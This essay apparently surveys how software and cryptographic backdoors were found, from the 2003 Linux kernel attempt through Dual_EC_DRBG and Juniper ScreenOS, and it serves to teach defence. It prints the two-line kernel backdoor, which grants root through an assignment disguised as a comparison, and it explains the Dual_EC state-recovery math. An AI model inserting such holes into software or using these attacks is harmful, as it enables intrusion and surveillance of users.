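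In this case, the attacker's mistakes made discovery harder, if anything. On a Mac, a faulty check usually made the malware skip the step that switches on remote login, so monitoring software had no attempt to record. OpenSourceMalware's *Trojanized Claude Code Extension Plants an SSH Backdoor* (2026) adds that the malware suppressed nearly all of its own errors and the real extension kept working, so users had no obvious fault, such as a frozen laptop, to investigate.

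Nobody has published a clear account of who noticed the backdoor first, or how. Cursor says that it "identified" the incident on 29 October and removed the extension "immediately upon detection". If the removal was immediate, the detection came shortly before 1:35 pm, about 11 hours after the malicious copy appeared. Cursor's notice does not credit anyone or say what first revealed the backdoor.

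Two outside groups published analyses on 30 October, after the removal. Hall writes that Phorion, a company that makes monitoring software for Macs, "detected" the backdoor, but does not say what set off the detection or whether Phorion alerted Cursor. OpenSourceMalware, which collects reports of malicious packages, thanks Dean Hardcastle, who "saw this happen in real time", but does not explain what he saw. An automated alarm is a reasonable guess, since the malware changed login keys, installed startup items and made outgoing connections, all of which monitoring software can record. But the public evidence does not confirm this, so the case should not count as a confirmed success for behavioural monitoring.

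The first reports also disagreed about where the malicious copy came from. OpenSourceMalware said its sample was from Open VSX, a separate public registry of extensions, but also said it had not established the sample's origin. Rojas (2026), in *Cursor traces marketplace breach to stolen Fireworks AI credential*, quotes Cursor's later explanation that an attacker had used a stolen credential to put the copies directly on the cache, the temporary store from which its marketplace served extensions. Le Monde Informatique's *Cursor : une clé volée chez Fireworks AI à l’origine d’une cyberattaque* (2026) dates Cursor's fuller report to 13 November and traces the breach to an access key compromised at Fireworks AI, one of Cursor's suppliers.

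According to Cursor, the attacker changed only the copy that the marketplace delivered, so reading Anthropic's source code would not have helped. OpenSourceMalware found that the malicious package matched the normal one except in a single file, where the attacker had inserted 66 lines before the genuine code. An integrity check comparing the marketplace's copy with Anthropic's would have revealed the difference, even if nobody understood the added lines.

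### Discovery by accident and by instrument

McMahon's accidental discovery reached PyPI by email 66 minutes after the upload of version 1.82.8, and no published account of tj-actions shows that the network monitor was faster. But this speed depended on the package's popularity. People normally install LiteLLM about 1,700 times a minute, so someone who will investigate a conspicuous fault soon encounters it. The same fault in an obscure package could take much longer to affect someone able to investigate it.

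McMahon also depended on the attackers making a mistake, as Freund had with XZ. A network monitor instead detects something the attack does, such as fetching a script, and records it even when nobody is watching. Monitors are therefore a better basis for policy, since a project can choose to install one but cannot count on attackers writing faulty code. The project has to install the monitor before the attack and have someone who responds to its alerts. One well-placed monitor can protect many other users, since StepSecurity needed only a single alert to warn every user of tj-actions.

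PyPI's main advice to developers after the LiteLLM attack makes automated scanners and monitors more important. PyPI recommends a "dependency cooldown", a setting that makes installation tools ignore any package released in the last few days. A three-day wait would have kept both malicious LiteLLM versions off a developer's machine, since PyPI quarantined them within hours. But McMahon found the malware because a tool had installed a release that was six minutes old. If most developers wait, fewer will find the next malicious release by accident, and the wait will protect them only if scanners and monitors find it before the cooldown ends.

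## The Linux kernel, 2003: two copies of the source that did not match

In November 2003 a routine integrity check caught an attempt to put a backdoor in the kernel, the core of the Linux operating system.

The kernel's developers kept their main repository in BitKeeper, a commercial program from the company BitMover. Some developers disliked BitKeeper, so BitMover also published a copy of the source in CVS, an older open-source system. Nobody was supposed to edit the CVS copy by hand. BitMover's founder, Larry McVoy, explained the export on the kernel mailing list (*BK2CVS problem*, 2003). BitMover converted the BitKeeper repository to CVS on an internal machine and copied the updated files to a public server. It then computed checksums, short values derived from a file's contents, on both machines and compared them. The comparison ran every night and sent an email if anything differed.

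On 5 November the comparison flagged one file, exit.c. Its history on the public server contained three extra entries, all dated the day before and under the name of David Miller, a well-known kernel developer. The first added two lines, the second removed 58, and the third put 58 back with the message "Oops, I worked on the the wrong file, fixed again." None of the entries had the reference number that the export process attached to every genuine change. Miller denied making them. McVoy ran tests to rule out a fault in BitMover's export program. By his count, BitMover found and corrected the problem in less than 24 hours.

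Accounts differ slightly on what first revealed the change. According to Princeton CITP's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003*, written ten years later, McVoy noticed the missing reference. According to McVoy's own messages and a news report from that week, *Attempted attack on Linux kernel foiled* (Lemos, 2003), the file comparison revealed it. The missing reference then helped to show that the change had not come from BitKeeper.

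### From a nuisance to a backdoor

McVoy's first message, at 20:45 UTC, reported that somebody had modified the CVS copy directly. It mentioned signs of a possible break-in, but it called the matter "not a big deal" and an annoyance for CVS users, and it left out the changed lines. Thirteen minutes later Matthew Dharm asked what they were, "out of curiosity". McVoy posted them at 22:23:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
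        retval = -EINVAL;
```

Zwane Mwaikambo replied, "That looks odd". At 22:48 Chad Kitching asked whether this was an attempt to backdoor the kernel. Three minutes later Andries Brouwer answered Mwaikambo, "Not if you hope to get root." Root is the administrator account, which has full control of the machine. McVoy agreed and added, "Good eyes, I missed that".

The lines were in the code for wait4, a system call that pauses a program until another one finishes. They look like a routine error check. The first line seems to test whether the calling program has chosen an odd combination of two options and is running as root, whose user number is 0. If both are true, the second line seems to reject the request as invalid.

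In the C programming language, two equals signs compare two values, while a single equals sign stores the value on the right in the variable on the left. The inserted code has two equals signs for the options but only one for the user number, so it makes the program root instead of testing whether it is already running as root.

C evaluates the second half of such a condition only if the first half is true, so ordinary uses of wait4 were unaffected. The assignment produces a zero, which C treats as "false", so the line that returns an error never ran. In Thomas and Francillon's terms, the odd combination of options was the trigger, the assignment was the payload, and root was the privileged state. An attacker already had to be able to run a program on the machine, so one reader wondered why the intruder hadn't tried to add a backdoor that worked remotely.

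Typing one equals sign instead of two is a familiar mistake in C. *Thwarted Linux backdoor hints at smarter hacks* (Poulsen, 2003) quotes the security consultant Ryan Russell, who called the code "indistinguishable from an accidental bug". But an accident was hard to believe, because someone had apparently broken into the server, bypassed the normal route for changes and used another developer's name. The integrity check therefore helped people judge intent, which might have been unclear from the code alone. Nobody has publicly identified the intruder.

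### What the comparison did and what reading did

The comparison worked well because the two copies should have been identical, so a single mismatch was enough to justify an investigation. McVoy told Lemos that finding the change took five minutes. In XZ, by contrast, legitimate differences hid the altered build file.

A checksum doesn't show what a change does, so people had to read the lines to find out. Kitching raised the possibility of a backdoor 25 minutes after McVoy posted the code. But they were reading two lines they already knew were unauthorised, which is far easier than finding the same two lines in the whole kernel.

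Even then, McVoy had missed the trick. Douglas Jones (2003), in *Thwarted Linux backdoor*, counts at least two very experienced programmers who at first saw only slightly odd code. The second is presumably Mwaikambo, who said soon afterwards that the remark had meant "that looks like fun", so Jones may have counted one too many. Jones points out that an automated check could have flagged the lines. The coding rules for US voting machines banned assignments inside conditions, and existing tools could find them. But Jones expected an attacker this skilled to write a backdoor that obeyed the rules.

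Some people saw the episode as a success for open source, because many people can inspect the code. McVoy, posting as lm (2003) in *One attempt thwarted*, called this "nonsense" and credited BitMover's habit of training its engineers to be paranoid. Another commenter replied that BitMover's engineers were among the many people inspecting the code and had found the problem first. McVoy's argument is stronger regarding the first sign of the problem, which came from a scheduled comparison and not from anyone reading the kernel. But other readers had only about a day to find the lines, so the case is weak evidence about whether they eventually would have.

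Developers disagreed about how dangerous the change had been. Linus Torvalds, who leads kernel development, said it could not have reached a release. Changes came to him either through BitKeeper, whose users would not have worked from the CVS copy, or as emailed patches. He said that patches to core files would be read and would need an explanation. McVoy thought that a developer using CVS could have unknowingly included the lines in a patch. Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, suggested that a Linux distribution might have built its kernel from the CVS copy.

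Torvalds was right that the attacker still had a long way to go. But catching the change on the email route depended on a reader noticing the missing equals sign, which McVoy had just failed to do in a two-line extract. BitKeeper offered stronger protection. Torvalds explained that if someone had tampered with the public BitKeeper copy, the next update from a private copy would have failed, because the public copy would have contained a change that the private one lacked.

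### Two altered downloads

Checksums and signatures also helped expose tampering with downloaded files. A digital signature lets anyone confirm that the holder of a particular private key signed that exact file.

In the first case, an attacker replaced the official release archive of vsFTPd, a file-transfer program, in 2011. On 3 July its author, Chris Evans, heard that the archive of version 2.3.4 appeared to contain a backdoor. He checked it against the signature made for the genuine release in February, and the check returned "BAD signature". In *vsftpd in the news*, Shnurapet (2011) quoted this result to Fedora's developers and asked whether their package-building process verified signatures.

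The signature confirmed the tampering, but it is less clear what first raised suspicion. Secunia, a security company, reported that Evans credited Mathias Kresin with the discovery, without explaining what Kresin had noticed. It could have been a failed checksum. According to FreeBSD Forums' *heads up vsftpd download backdoored*, the altered archive did not match the checksum that the FreeBSD operating system had on record. Threatpost's *Vsftpd FTP Server Download Site Compromised* reports that Evans thought any major redistributor was almost certain to notice the problem.

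The altered archive was available for two to three days. In *vsftpd download backdoored*, Solar Designer (2011) found dates inside the archive suggesting that it was altered no earlier than 30 June, assuming the intruder's clock was right. According to a follow-up message that Moore (2011) quotes in the same thread, a copy on a mirror site in Namibia showed that it was altered by 1 July at the latest. The attacker had apparently given the file the same February date as the genuine release, which might have fooled someone who looked only at dates. A checksum would still have revealed the change because it depends on the file's contents. Solar Designer called the case "a great example" of why maintainers should sign their releases and distributions should check the signatures.

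The second case lasted much longer. Codecov reports how much of a program its tests cover. Its customers' automated build jobs downloaded a script, the Bash Uploader, to send in their results. Codecov's *Bash Uploader Security Update* (2021) describes how an attacker added a line to the script that copied the job's stored settings, including any passwords and access keys, to an outside server. Like the tj-actions attack, this was theft, not a backdoor in the strict sense.

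On 1 April 2021 a customer computed the checksum of the downloaded script and found that it differed from the one Codecov published on GitHub. Someone had first altered the script on 31 January. Codecov counted 108 separate periods in which the site served the altered version, so a customer who checked only once might have received a clean copy.

Any customer could have made the same comparison during those two months, but Codecov's *Post-Mortem / Root Cause Analysis (April 2021)* (2021) acknowledges that the company had never fully documented how to do it. After the attack, Codecov set up alerts for any change to the script, so detection no longer depended on a careful customer. BitMover had already automated its comparison in 2003, which largely explains why its altered file lasted about a day and Codecov's altered script two months.

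In all three cases the attacker changed the file but not the reference it was checked against. BitMover's reference copy was on an internal machine, Evans's signature required a private key, and Codecov's checksum was on GitHub while the script was on a different service. An intruder who can replace both a file and its published checksum can make them match.

### Matching copies of malicious code

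A valid checksum or signature shows that a file has not changed since somebody recorded its checksum or signed it. The file may already have been malicious by then. At SolarWinds, for example, attackers altered the code during the build, before the company signed it.

A more recent attack shows the same weakness in provenance, a signed record of the source and build system that produced a package. On 11 May 2026, attackers published 84 malicious package files under the name of TanStack, a family of JavaScript libraries, all with valid provenance. SLSA's *Mini Shai-Hulud* (2026) explains that the attackers ran their code inside TanStack's release process and used its identity to publish. The records correctly named the project's repository and build service, and nobody could have told them apart from those on genuine packages.

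SLSA argues that a build platform with stricter separation between jobs would have blocked this route, and that an independent rebuild from the same source could have revealed a different result. It also points out that the jobs that published the packages had failed, so an alert for packages published by failed jobs could have shortened the exposure by hours without any analysis of the packages.

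Integrity checks are least useful when the person adding the backdoor is allowed to change the code. Jia Tan's signatures on the XZ archives were genuine. Likewise, if a trusted kernel developer had submitted the two lines in 2003 and Torvalds had accepted them, BitMover would have exported them to CVS, and the two copies would have matched in the nightly comparison.

Ts'o raised a similar worry in the 2003 discussion. Someone could forge a sender's address and email Torvalds a security hole disguised as a bug fix, hidden among plausible changes. Ts'o wanted a digital signature on every change, and McVoy already had a design. Signatures would have made it harder to pose as Miller, but they would not have stopped Miller, or anyone else with a valid key, from signing a malicious change.

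Version 1.2 of the SLSA specification adds records of how each change entered a repository, including whether it met the project's review requirements. These records can show that a review took place, but not that the reviewer understood the code. SLSA's *Threats & mitigations* leaves users to find another reason to trust that a producer isn't malicious, such as an active community that may spot bad code or a supplier with a reputation to lose. It calls this "a judgement call with no straightforward answer".

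## Dual_EC_DRBG, 2007 to 2015: cryptographers' suspicion and leaked documents

The US National Security Agency (NSA), which intercepts foreign communications and also helps to protect American ones, supplied Dual_EC_DRBG, a method of generating random numbers. It was one of four methods in a standard that NIST, the US standards institute, published in June 2006. Cryptographers questioned whether the people who chose two constants printed in the standard had kept a secret about them. If they had, a program could have a backdoor even if it followed the standard exactly and anyone could read its code, so users had to trust the NSA.

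### Why encryption needs unpredictable numbers

Encryption scrambles a message so that only someone with the right key, a secret number, can read it. The method is normally public so that experts can test it, and secrecy depends on the key. An eavesdropper who can predict the key can read the message without finding any fault in the method.

Computers collect only a little true randomness from physical processes. As Bernstein, Lange and Niederhagen (2015) explain in *Dual EC*, a pseudorandom number generator stretches this into a long supply of random-looking numbers. The generator keeps a secret number called its internal state. When a program requests random data, the generator calculates an output from the state, then a new state to replace the old one. These calculations involve no chance, so anyone who learns the state can work out every later output until the generator takes in fresh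 randomness.

Programs send some of these outputs openly. When a browser connects to a secure website, for example, the two computers exchange random values unencrypted before they agree on a key, and the secret numbers behind that key may come from the same generator. It must therefore be practically impossible to work out the generator's state from an output. Otherwise, a single public value can expose the keys that protect web traffic, email and anything else that relies on the generator.

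### Two points and a secret number

Dual_EC_DRBG uses an elliptic curve, which here means a huge but finite set of points whose coordinates, x and y, satisfy a fixed equation. There is a rule for adding points, and adding together s copies of a point P gives the point sP. A computer can calculate sP quickly even when s is an enormous whole number, but nobody has published a practical way to find s from P and sP on these curves.

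The standard supplies two fixed points, P and Q. In its smallest version the state, s, is a 256-bit number, and each step has two parts:

- Output: multiply Q by s, take the x-coordinate of the result, discard its first 16 bits and release the other 240, which make 30 bytes.
- New state: multiply P by s and take the x-coordinate of the result.

Someone who sees the output knows most of the x-coordinate of sQ. The new state comes from sP, so this should be no help. But the number of points on the curve is prime, which means that each of the two points is a multiple of the other. Some number e therefore satisfies P = eQ, and anyone who knows e can get from one result to the other:

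e(sQ) = s(eQ) = sP

Dan Shumow and Niels Ferguson, two cryptographers at Microsoft, presented this calculation in a short talk at the Crypto conference in August 2007. According to their slides, *On the Possibility of a Back Door*, the 16 discarded bits add little work. They leave 65,536 possible x-coordinates, about half of which belong to points on the curve. Multiplying each of those points by e gives about 32,000 candidates for the new state, and the next two bytes of output identify the right one.

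Nobody has a practical way to calculate e from the published P and Q alone. But whoever produced Q could have chosen a secret number d, set Q = dP, and then easily calculated e from d. Shumow and Ferguson tested this with a Q of their own, and in every experiment 32 bytes of output were enough to identify the state. They could not run the test on the official Q because they did not know its secret number.

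They said they were not accusing NIST of deliberately planting a backdoor, and that they did not know whether the designer had d or e. They had proved only that a backdoor was possible and that its key existed as a number, whether or not anybody knew it.

Reading the code of a product that used the generator would not have revealed who held the key. The code contained no secret password or suspicious branch, only the arithmetic and the two points, and both would have passed an integrity check against the standard. Monitoring the program's behaviour would not have helped either, because the program ran the same way whether or not anyone knew e. An eavesdropper only had to record public traffic and do the calculation elsewhere.

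### Objections in 2006 and 2007

Cryptographers had already found a different fault. In March 2006 Kristian Gjøsteen, a Norwegian researcher, sent NIST a paper showing that the generator's output was biased, meaning that it differed slightly from truly random bits. Berry Schoenmakers and Andrey Sidorenko, in the Netherlands, improved on this result in May and called the generator insecure. The bias alone did not give anyone access to encrypted messages, and Gjøsteen considered its practical impact modest. But it meant that the generator's output could be distinguished from random data, which is not supposed to be possible.

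The obvious remedy was to discard many more bits at each step. Bernstein and colleagues note that this would also have closed the backdoor, which nobody had yet announced publicly. Shumow and Ferguson later suggested discarding about half the bits. An eavesdropper would then have had to guess 128 missing bits instead of 16, which is far beyond what any computer can do. NIST published the standard in June 2006 without this change.

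The 2007 talk reached a wider audience that November, when the security writer Bruce Schneier described it in Wired. In *The Strange Story of Dual_EC_DRBG*, Schneier (2007) argued that the generator made no sense as engineering because it was too slow for anyone to use willingly. He advised readers to avoid it "under any circumstances" and called on NIST and the NSA to explain themselves. NIST replied in a letter that it had "no evidence that anyone has, or will ever have," the secret numbers, so it was not withdrawing the algorithm.

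### The leaked memos and the RSA contract

Nearly six years later, on 5 September 2013, the Guardian, the New York Times and ProPublica reported on classified documents from Edward Snowden, a former NSA contractor. The joint report, *The NSA's Secret Campaign to Crack, Undermine Internet Encryption* by Ball, Borger and colleagues, describes a programme, costing more than $250 million a year, in which the NSA worked with technology companies to make their products "exploitable". One of the NSA's goals in its 2013 budget request was to influence standards for commercial encryption.

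The report almost certainly means Dual_EC_DRBG, though it does not name it. It describes a standard that NIST adopted in 2006 and in which two Microsoft cryptographers discovered a "fatal weakness" in 2007. According to the reporters, NSA memos "appear to confirm" that the agency engineered the weakness. According to one memo they quote, the NSA eventually became the standard's "sole editor". They also report that the agency privately called its effort to win international approval "a challenge in finesse".

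The Office of the Director of National Intelligence responded the next day. It said that deciphering communications was a known part of the NSA's mission and complained that the stories had revealed classified details. It did not address the claim about the standard.

On 10 September NIST reopened the standard for public comment, and that month it advised people to stop using the generator. In April 2014 it removed the generator from its draft guidance, citing "its own evaluation" and "the lack of public confidence in the algorithm" (NIST, 2014). It published the final revision in June 2015. In its announcement, NIST mentioned only concerns that the algorithm "might contain a weakness", so the withdrawal was not an official finding that the NSA had planted a backdoor.

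Meanwhile, the reports had drawn attention to products that used the generator, which was the default in BSAFE, a widely used set of encryption tools from the company RSA. In December 2013, Joseph Menn (2013) of Reuters reported in *Secret contract tied NSA and security industry pioneer* that RSA had received $10 million in a deal that made the generator BSAFE's preferred option, citing two people familiar with the contract. The sum was more than a third of what the relevant RSA division had earned in the previous year.

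RSA declined to answer Menn's questions, but said in a statement that it never designed or enabled backdoors in its products. It did not address the payment in the statement, and the NSA declined to comment. Several current and former employees told Menn that government officials had misled RSA by presenting the generator as an advance in security. At least nine speakers withdrew from the company's annual conference, according to ASIS's *RSA Executive Chairman Addresses NSA Allegations at Cyber Conference* (2014). RSA's chairman, Arthur Coviello, said at the conference that the press had left out crucial details that favoured the company.

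If Menn's sources are right, the payment shows that the NSA wanted people to use the generator, but not that RSA knew of a backdoor. The cryptographer Matthew Green allows in *The strange story of “Extended Random”* that RSA could have chosen the generator innocently, since it was part of a NIST standard.

### How strong the evidence of intent is

The memos are the most direct evidence, but the public knows them mainly through the reporters' descriptions and a few quoted phrases. The news organisations withheld some details after intelligence officials asked them not to publish, and the reporters hedged with the words "appear to confirm". Their news report also dates international approval after NIST's, although the International Organization for Standardization (ISO) had included the generator in a standard in 2005.

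Other records support the reporters' account of events at ISO. In 2003 ISO was far along with a standard that did not include Dual_EC_DRBG, and 19 of the 24 voting countries had approved the draft. Bernstein and colleagues found that only the United States objected to the whole document. It submitted a 153-page replacement containing the generator, with the same P and Q that NIST later adopted, and ISO agreed to use it.

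Emails released in 2014 show that John Kelsey, a NIST cryptographer working on the standard, asked Don Johnson in October 2004 where the point Q came from. Johnson, who had presented the generator at a workshop, replied that Q was in essence "the public key for some random private key". That private key would be the secret number d. Johnson added that Q could have been generated another way, but that the NSA had "kyboshed" the idea and forbidden him to discuss it publicly. That method would have made it much harder for the designers to know d. Kelsey wrote in 2014 that he had not seen at the time why this mattered.

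When Ferguson raised the problem with the American standards committee in 2005, the NSA answered that it had generated the points "in a secure, classified way". The agency wanted existing devices that used these points to qualify for government certification, but it was willing to let other users choose their own. NIST added instructions for doing so, but the standard advised against it, and only products with the official points could be certified. Kelsey reports in his December 2013 slides, *800-90 and Dual EC DRBG*, that as far as NIST knew, nobody had used their own points.

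Richard George, a former technical director at the NSA, gave the fullest defence in a talk in May 2014. He said the agency wanted the generator for its own use and assumed nobody else would choose something so slow and ugly. This could explain why the NSA asked for certification of its own points, but not why it stopped Johnson from discussing a safer way to generate Q. It is also hard to reconcile with a $10 million contract to make the generator a default. In 2015 Bernstein and colleagues knew of no public NSA comment on the restriction or the contract.

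Writers who know the evidence well still describe it differently. Kostyuk and Landau (2022), in *Dueling over Dual_EC_DRBG*, treat the NSA's backdoor as an established fact. Kelsey (2015), in *Dual EC DRBG and NIST Crypto Process Review*, writes only that the NSA "is alleged" to have chosen the points so that it would know a backdoor. The combined evidence makes an innocent explanation unlikely but is not proof. Nobody has published the secret number, and the September 2013 report does not identify any message that the NSA decrypted with it.

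If the secret number e leaked, most of the doubt would be gone, because anyone could quickly check whether eQ equals P. The NSA would find it much harder to prove that it does not have e. If it had derived Q from a published string of text by a published procedure, outsiders could have repeated the steps and checked that no one had started from a secret number. Because the procedure was classified, even a designer who had destroyed e could not prove having done so.

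### Why the 2007 warning had so little effect

Cryptographers knew of the weakness before the leak. Two employees of the Canadian company Certicom, Daniel Brown and Scott Vanstone, had described it in a patent application in January 2005, and the full text of a later application appeared online in July 2006, a month after NIST published the standard. Cryptographers readily accepted the mathematics of the 2007 talk. Hal Finney (2007) called it "a very nice piece of analysis" in *Possible backdoor in FIPS SP 800-90 PRNG*, a message to a cryptography mailing list. But the generator stayed in the standard until after the press reports.

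One reason is that outside experts thought the generator was no longer a concern. It was thousands of times slower than the alternatives and had a bad reputation, and Bernstein and colleagues recall that by the end of 2007 cryptographers regarded it as "dead and gone". In fact, dozens of commercial software libraries offered it, many of them on NIST's public list of certified products, and Juniper used it in its network equipment. According to Green, RSA had not hidden that the generator was its default, but the choice was so strange that no cryptographer had noticed.

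Many people also found a deliberate backdoor hard to believe. In the 2007 discussion *Is there a backdoor in NIST's SP800-90 Dual Ec pseudorandom number generator?*, one person accused the NSA of an incompetent attempt to "screw everyone over", while another thought that was unfair and a backdoor unlikely. Once someone had pointed out the weakness, it was so easy to describe that an intelligence agency might have seemed too clever to rely on it.

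NIST let this doubt settle the matter by asking for the wrong kind of evidence. Kostyuk and Landau write that it asked whether anyone had corrupted the generator, and found no sign of this, when it should have asked whether anyone could have. Outsiders could answer only the second question. Proving that someone held the secret number would have taken a disclosure by the holder, a leak, or a mathematical breakthrough. By waiting for such proof, NIST in effect gave the designer of the constants the benefit of the doubt.

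That might have been reasonable if precautions had been difficult, but they would have been easy. The standard already contained three other generators. NIST could also have recommended a new Q from a verifiable procedure and kept the NSA's as an option for existing devices. Kelsey calls new, verifiably random points the "obvious choice", and says the committee rejected them because at least one company had already built a product with the original points and the danger "didn't seem like a real threat".

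The people making this decision depended on the NSA for advice. According to Kostyuk and Landau, NIST had only four cryptographers when it approved the generator. Kelsey lists reliance on the NSA's expertise in elliptic curves among the causes of the failure. In one draft, he wrote "here's the limit of my competence" and asked for someone with the right background, such as "one of the NSA guys", to check the passage. The published standard listed only two authors, both NIST employees, so most readers could not tell from the title page how much of it came from the NSA.

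Much of the early work had also taken place where few academics could see it. The generator first went through the American National Standards Institute (ANSI), whose membership fees kept most universities out, and through ISO, which admits only national standards bodies. Kelsey says the editing committee ignored or played down outside comments. Those who knew about the weakness did not always raise it forcefully. Brown later said Certicom had first tried to disclose it "quietly", through the patent, and that the later publicity had seemed sufficient. Brown had expected that publicity to make NIST withdraw the points.

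The mathematical case against Dual_EC_DRBG was the same in 2013 as in 2007, but the leaked memos gave people a reason to think that somebody had the secret number. NIST reopened the standard five days after the first report. But investigators cannot count on such leaks. Snowden obtained dozens of documents about the NSA's decryption programme although, the reporters believed, he had not been cleared for it.

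NIST has since promised to name NSA co-authors and answer every comment publicly, and by 2019 it had more than tripled its number of cryptographers. In 2015 Kelsey thought the procedural changes might help prevent a repeat but were "mostly" not enough. Kelsey put more weight on independent expertise, a different relationship with the NSA, and recognizing that well-funded attackers, including insiders, may try to weaken a standard while helping to write it.

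## Juniper ScreenOS, 2015: an internal review and outsiders comparing firmware

On 17 December 2015 the network equipment maker Juniper Networks announced that an "internal code review" had found unauthorised code in ScreenOS, the operating system of its NetScreen firewalls. These devices controlled what traffic could enter a network and ran virtual private networks (VPNs), which encrypt traffic as it crosses the internet. Worrall (2015), in *Important Announcement about ScreenOS*, warned that a knowledgeable attacker could take control of the devices and decrypt VPN connections. Juniper had received no reports of anyone doing so.

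Juniper has not publicly explained why it carried out the review. When Tom's Hardware asked about a possible link to a leaked NSA catalogue, Juniper repeated its announcement (*Juniper Finds Backdoor In NetScreen Firewalls*). In a letter to Senator Ron Wyden, Juniper Networks (2020) wrote that it "became aware" of an attacker in one of its internal networks, but did not say whether it learned of the attacker before or after the review. The review may have been routine, or a tip or signs of a break-in may have prompted it. By Juniper's account, source review confirmed the backdoors, but the first sign of them is unknown.

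### A master password and readable VPN traffic

The first backdoor was a fixed password. Anyone who entered it with any username over SSH or Telnet, an older remote-login system, got full control of the firewall. The security company Rapid7 (2015) found about 26,000 NetScreen devices that accepted SSH connections from the internet. The password resembled the debugging messages elsewhere in the program, so someone reading the code could easily have missed it.

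Juniper did not say in its first advisory which affected versions had which backdoor. Rapid7 searched several older releases for the password and could not find it. Juniper then confirmed that only versions 6.3.0r17 to 6.3.0r20 contained it.

Sources disagree about when Juniper first shipped the password. *Where Did I Leave My Keys?* (Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues, 2018) dates version 6.3.0r17 to April 2013 but warns that Juniper's release notes, file dates and website do not agree precisely. Rapid7 suggests late 2013. Bloomberg's *Juniper Breach Mystery Starts to Clear With New Details on Hackers* (2021) cites an internal Juniper document that puts the change in 2014. A June 2014 vulnerability record, Positive Technologies' *PT-2014-5520*, lists the same version as the fix for an unrelated fault, which fits a 2014 release better than one a year earlier. Customers therefore had the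 password on their firewalls for at least 18 months and perhaps 32.

The second backdoor let an eavesdropper decrypt VPN traffic without connecting to the firewall. It was in releases r15 to r18 of version 6.2.0 and releases r12 to r20 of version 6.3.0. Checkoway and colleagues date the earliest of these to August 2012, so Juniper shipped this backdoor for about three years and four months.

### Comparing the old and new firmware

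Outsiders did not have the ScreenOS source code, but they could compare the firmware from before and after Juniper's repairs. Along with new versions, Juniper published copies of older ones rebuilt without the backdoors. According to Rapid7, these copies were the best candidates for analysis because they had very few other changes.

Rapid7's analysts unpacked the firmware and loaded it into a tool that displays a binary's machine instructions. In the old version, a function that checked administrators' logins compared some text with a fixed string, which was the password. The repaired version did not make this comparison. An employee of Fox-IT, another security company, reported finding the password within six hours. Attackers could also compare the two firmware versions, so releasing the repair increased the risk to customers who had not yet installed it.

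The VPN backdoor was harder to interpret. ImperialViolet's *Juniper* (2015) records researchers' conversations over the two days after the announcement. They extracted the readable text from both firmware versions and noticed that one long number had changed. The numbers just before it were the published parameters of a standard elliptic curve, so the changed number probably had a cryptographic purpose too.

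The researchers first considered whether an attacker had switched the firewall to a weaker curve, but that would not have made the traffic readable in real time. They also guessed at a key for checking signatures, but that did not explain the decryption either. Then Ralf-Philipp Weinmann found an error message nearby that mentioned an "EC PRNG", an elliptic-curve random-number generator. This pointed to Dual_EC_DRBG. Anyone who knows the secret number linking that generator's constants, P and Q, can predict its output. Juniper had already stated on its website that ScreenOS used Dual_EC_DRBG with its own constants.

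The changed number was the x-coordinate of Q. Checkoway and colleagues found only one other change in the generator, to the expected output stored for a self-test. Nobody outside can prove that the intruder knew the secret number for the new Q, but there is little other reason to replace Q.

### Why one constant was enough

According to Juniper, a new Q should not have exposed any traffic. In October 2013, after the Snowden reports had drawn attention to Dual_EC_DRBG, the company published an article describing two safeguards. It said ScreenOS used Juniper's own constants instead of the NSA's and passed the output through a second generator, X9.31, before using it. The second generator would keep an eavesdropper from seeing the raw output needed to work out the first generator's state.

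Both safeguards had already failed. Current releases had used the intruder's Q for about a year. Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues showed in *A Systematic Analysis of the Juniper Dual EC Incident* (2016) that X9.31 never ran in the default configuration.

The program was supposed to take a fresh starting value from Dual_EC_DRBG and then fill a 32-byte area of memory with X9.31 output, eight bytes at a time, until a counter passed 31. But the routine that fetched the starting value used the same counter and left it at 32, so the loop that called X9.31 never ran. The routine had also used that area of memory for its own work, so the program sent out the raw Dual_EC_DRBG output still stored there.

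Several experienced researchers who knew that the routine probably contained a bug still missed this mistake until Willem Pinckaers pointed out the shared counter. The laboratory that evaluated ScreenOS for US government certification also failed to notice that X9.31, the generator named in the certificate, never ran. Checkoway and colleagues suggest that coverage analysis, which records which parts of a program run, might have revealed the problem. That check would not have required anyone to understand the loop.

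Outside researchers compared dozens of ScreenOS releases and traced the mistake to version 6.2, which Juniper released in October 2008. Several other changes in that version also helped an eavesdropper.

| Feature | Version 6.1 | Version 6.2 | Effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| Source of starting values for X9.31 | Randomness collected by the device | Dual_EC_DRBG | Made a secret number for Q useful |
| How often X9.31 got a new starting value | Every 10,000 calls | Every call | Made the faulty step run every time |
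| Loop counter and output memory | Not shared with the routine that fetched starting values | Shared with it | Released raw Dual_EC_DRBG output |
| Random value sent openly when a VPN connection starts | 20 bytes | 32 bytes | Revealed enough output for the attack, which needs about 26 bytes |
| When the device generated that value | When needed | In advance, usually before the connection's secret key | Often allowed decryption of a connection from its own traffic alone |

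The attack needed the first four changes, and the fifth made it more practical. As far as Checkoway and colleagues know, Juniper's own engineers made all five. Each could have had an innocent purpose. For instance, Dual_EC_DRBG was slow, and preparing random values in advance speeds up new connections. But Juniper has not explained how it designed the system or how it produced its original Q. If someone kept the secret number for that Q, they could have read VPN traffic starting in 2008, four years before the intruder's change.

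To test their analysis, the team bought a NetScreen device and installed firmware with a Q whose secret number they knew. They set up three kinds of VPN connection and decrypted each one using only its own recorded traffic. The attack does not work against every configuration. For example, a strong shared password would still protect a connection that used the older version of the key-exchange protocol.

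### Who asked for the generator and who changed the constant

Juniper told members of Congress that it had added Dual_EC_DRBG "at the request of a customer", but would not identify the customer, according to *Lynch Joins Letter Questioning NSA Response Following Supply Chain Hacks*, from the office of Representative Stephen Lynch. Reuters had reported in October 2020 that Juniper told the researcher Andy Isaacson much the same in a 2016 message.

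Bloomberg identifies the customer as the US Department of Defense, citing a former senior intelligence official and three Juniper employees who were involved in the decision or briefed about it. They said the department made the generator a condition of some future contracts, and Juniper's engineers knew some experts suspected a backdoor. The department declined to discuss its relationship with Juniper. Juniper has acknowledged the request, but only unnamed sources link it to the department.

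It is also not publicly known whether the NSA had any part in choosing Juniper's constants. Lawmakers asked the agency about this in 2021. Wyden's staff say NSA officials told them in 2018 about a "lessons learned" report on the generator, but that the agency later said it could not find the document.

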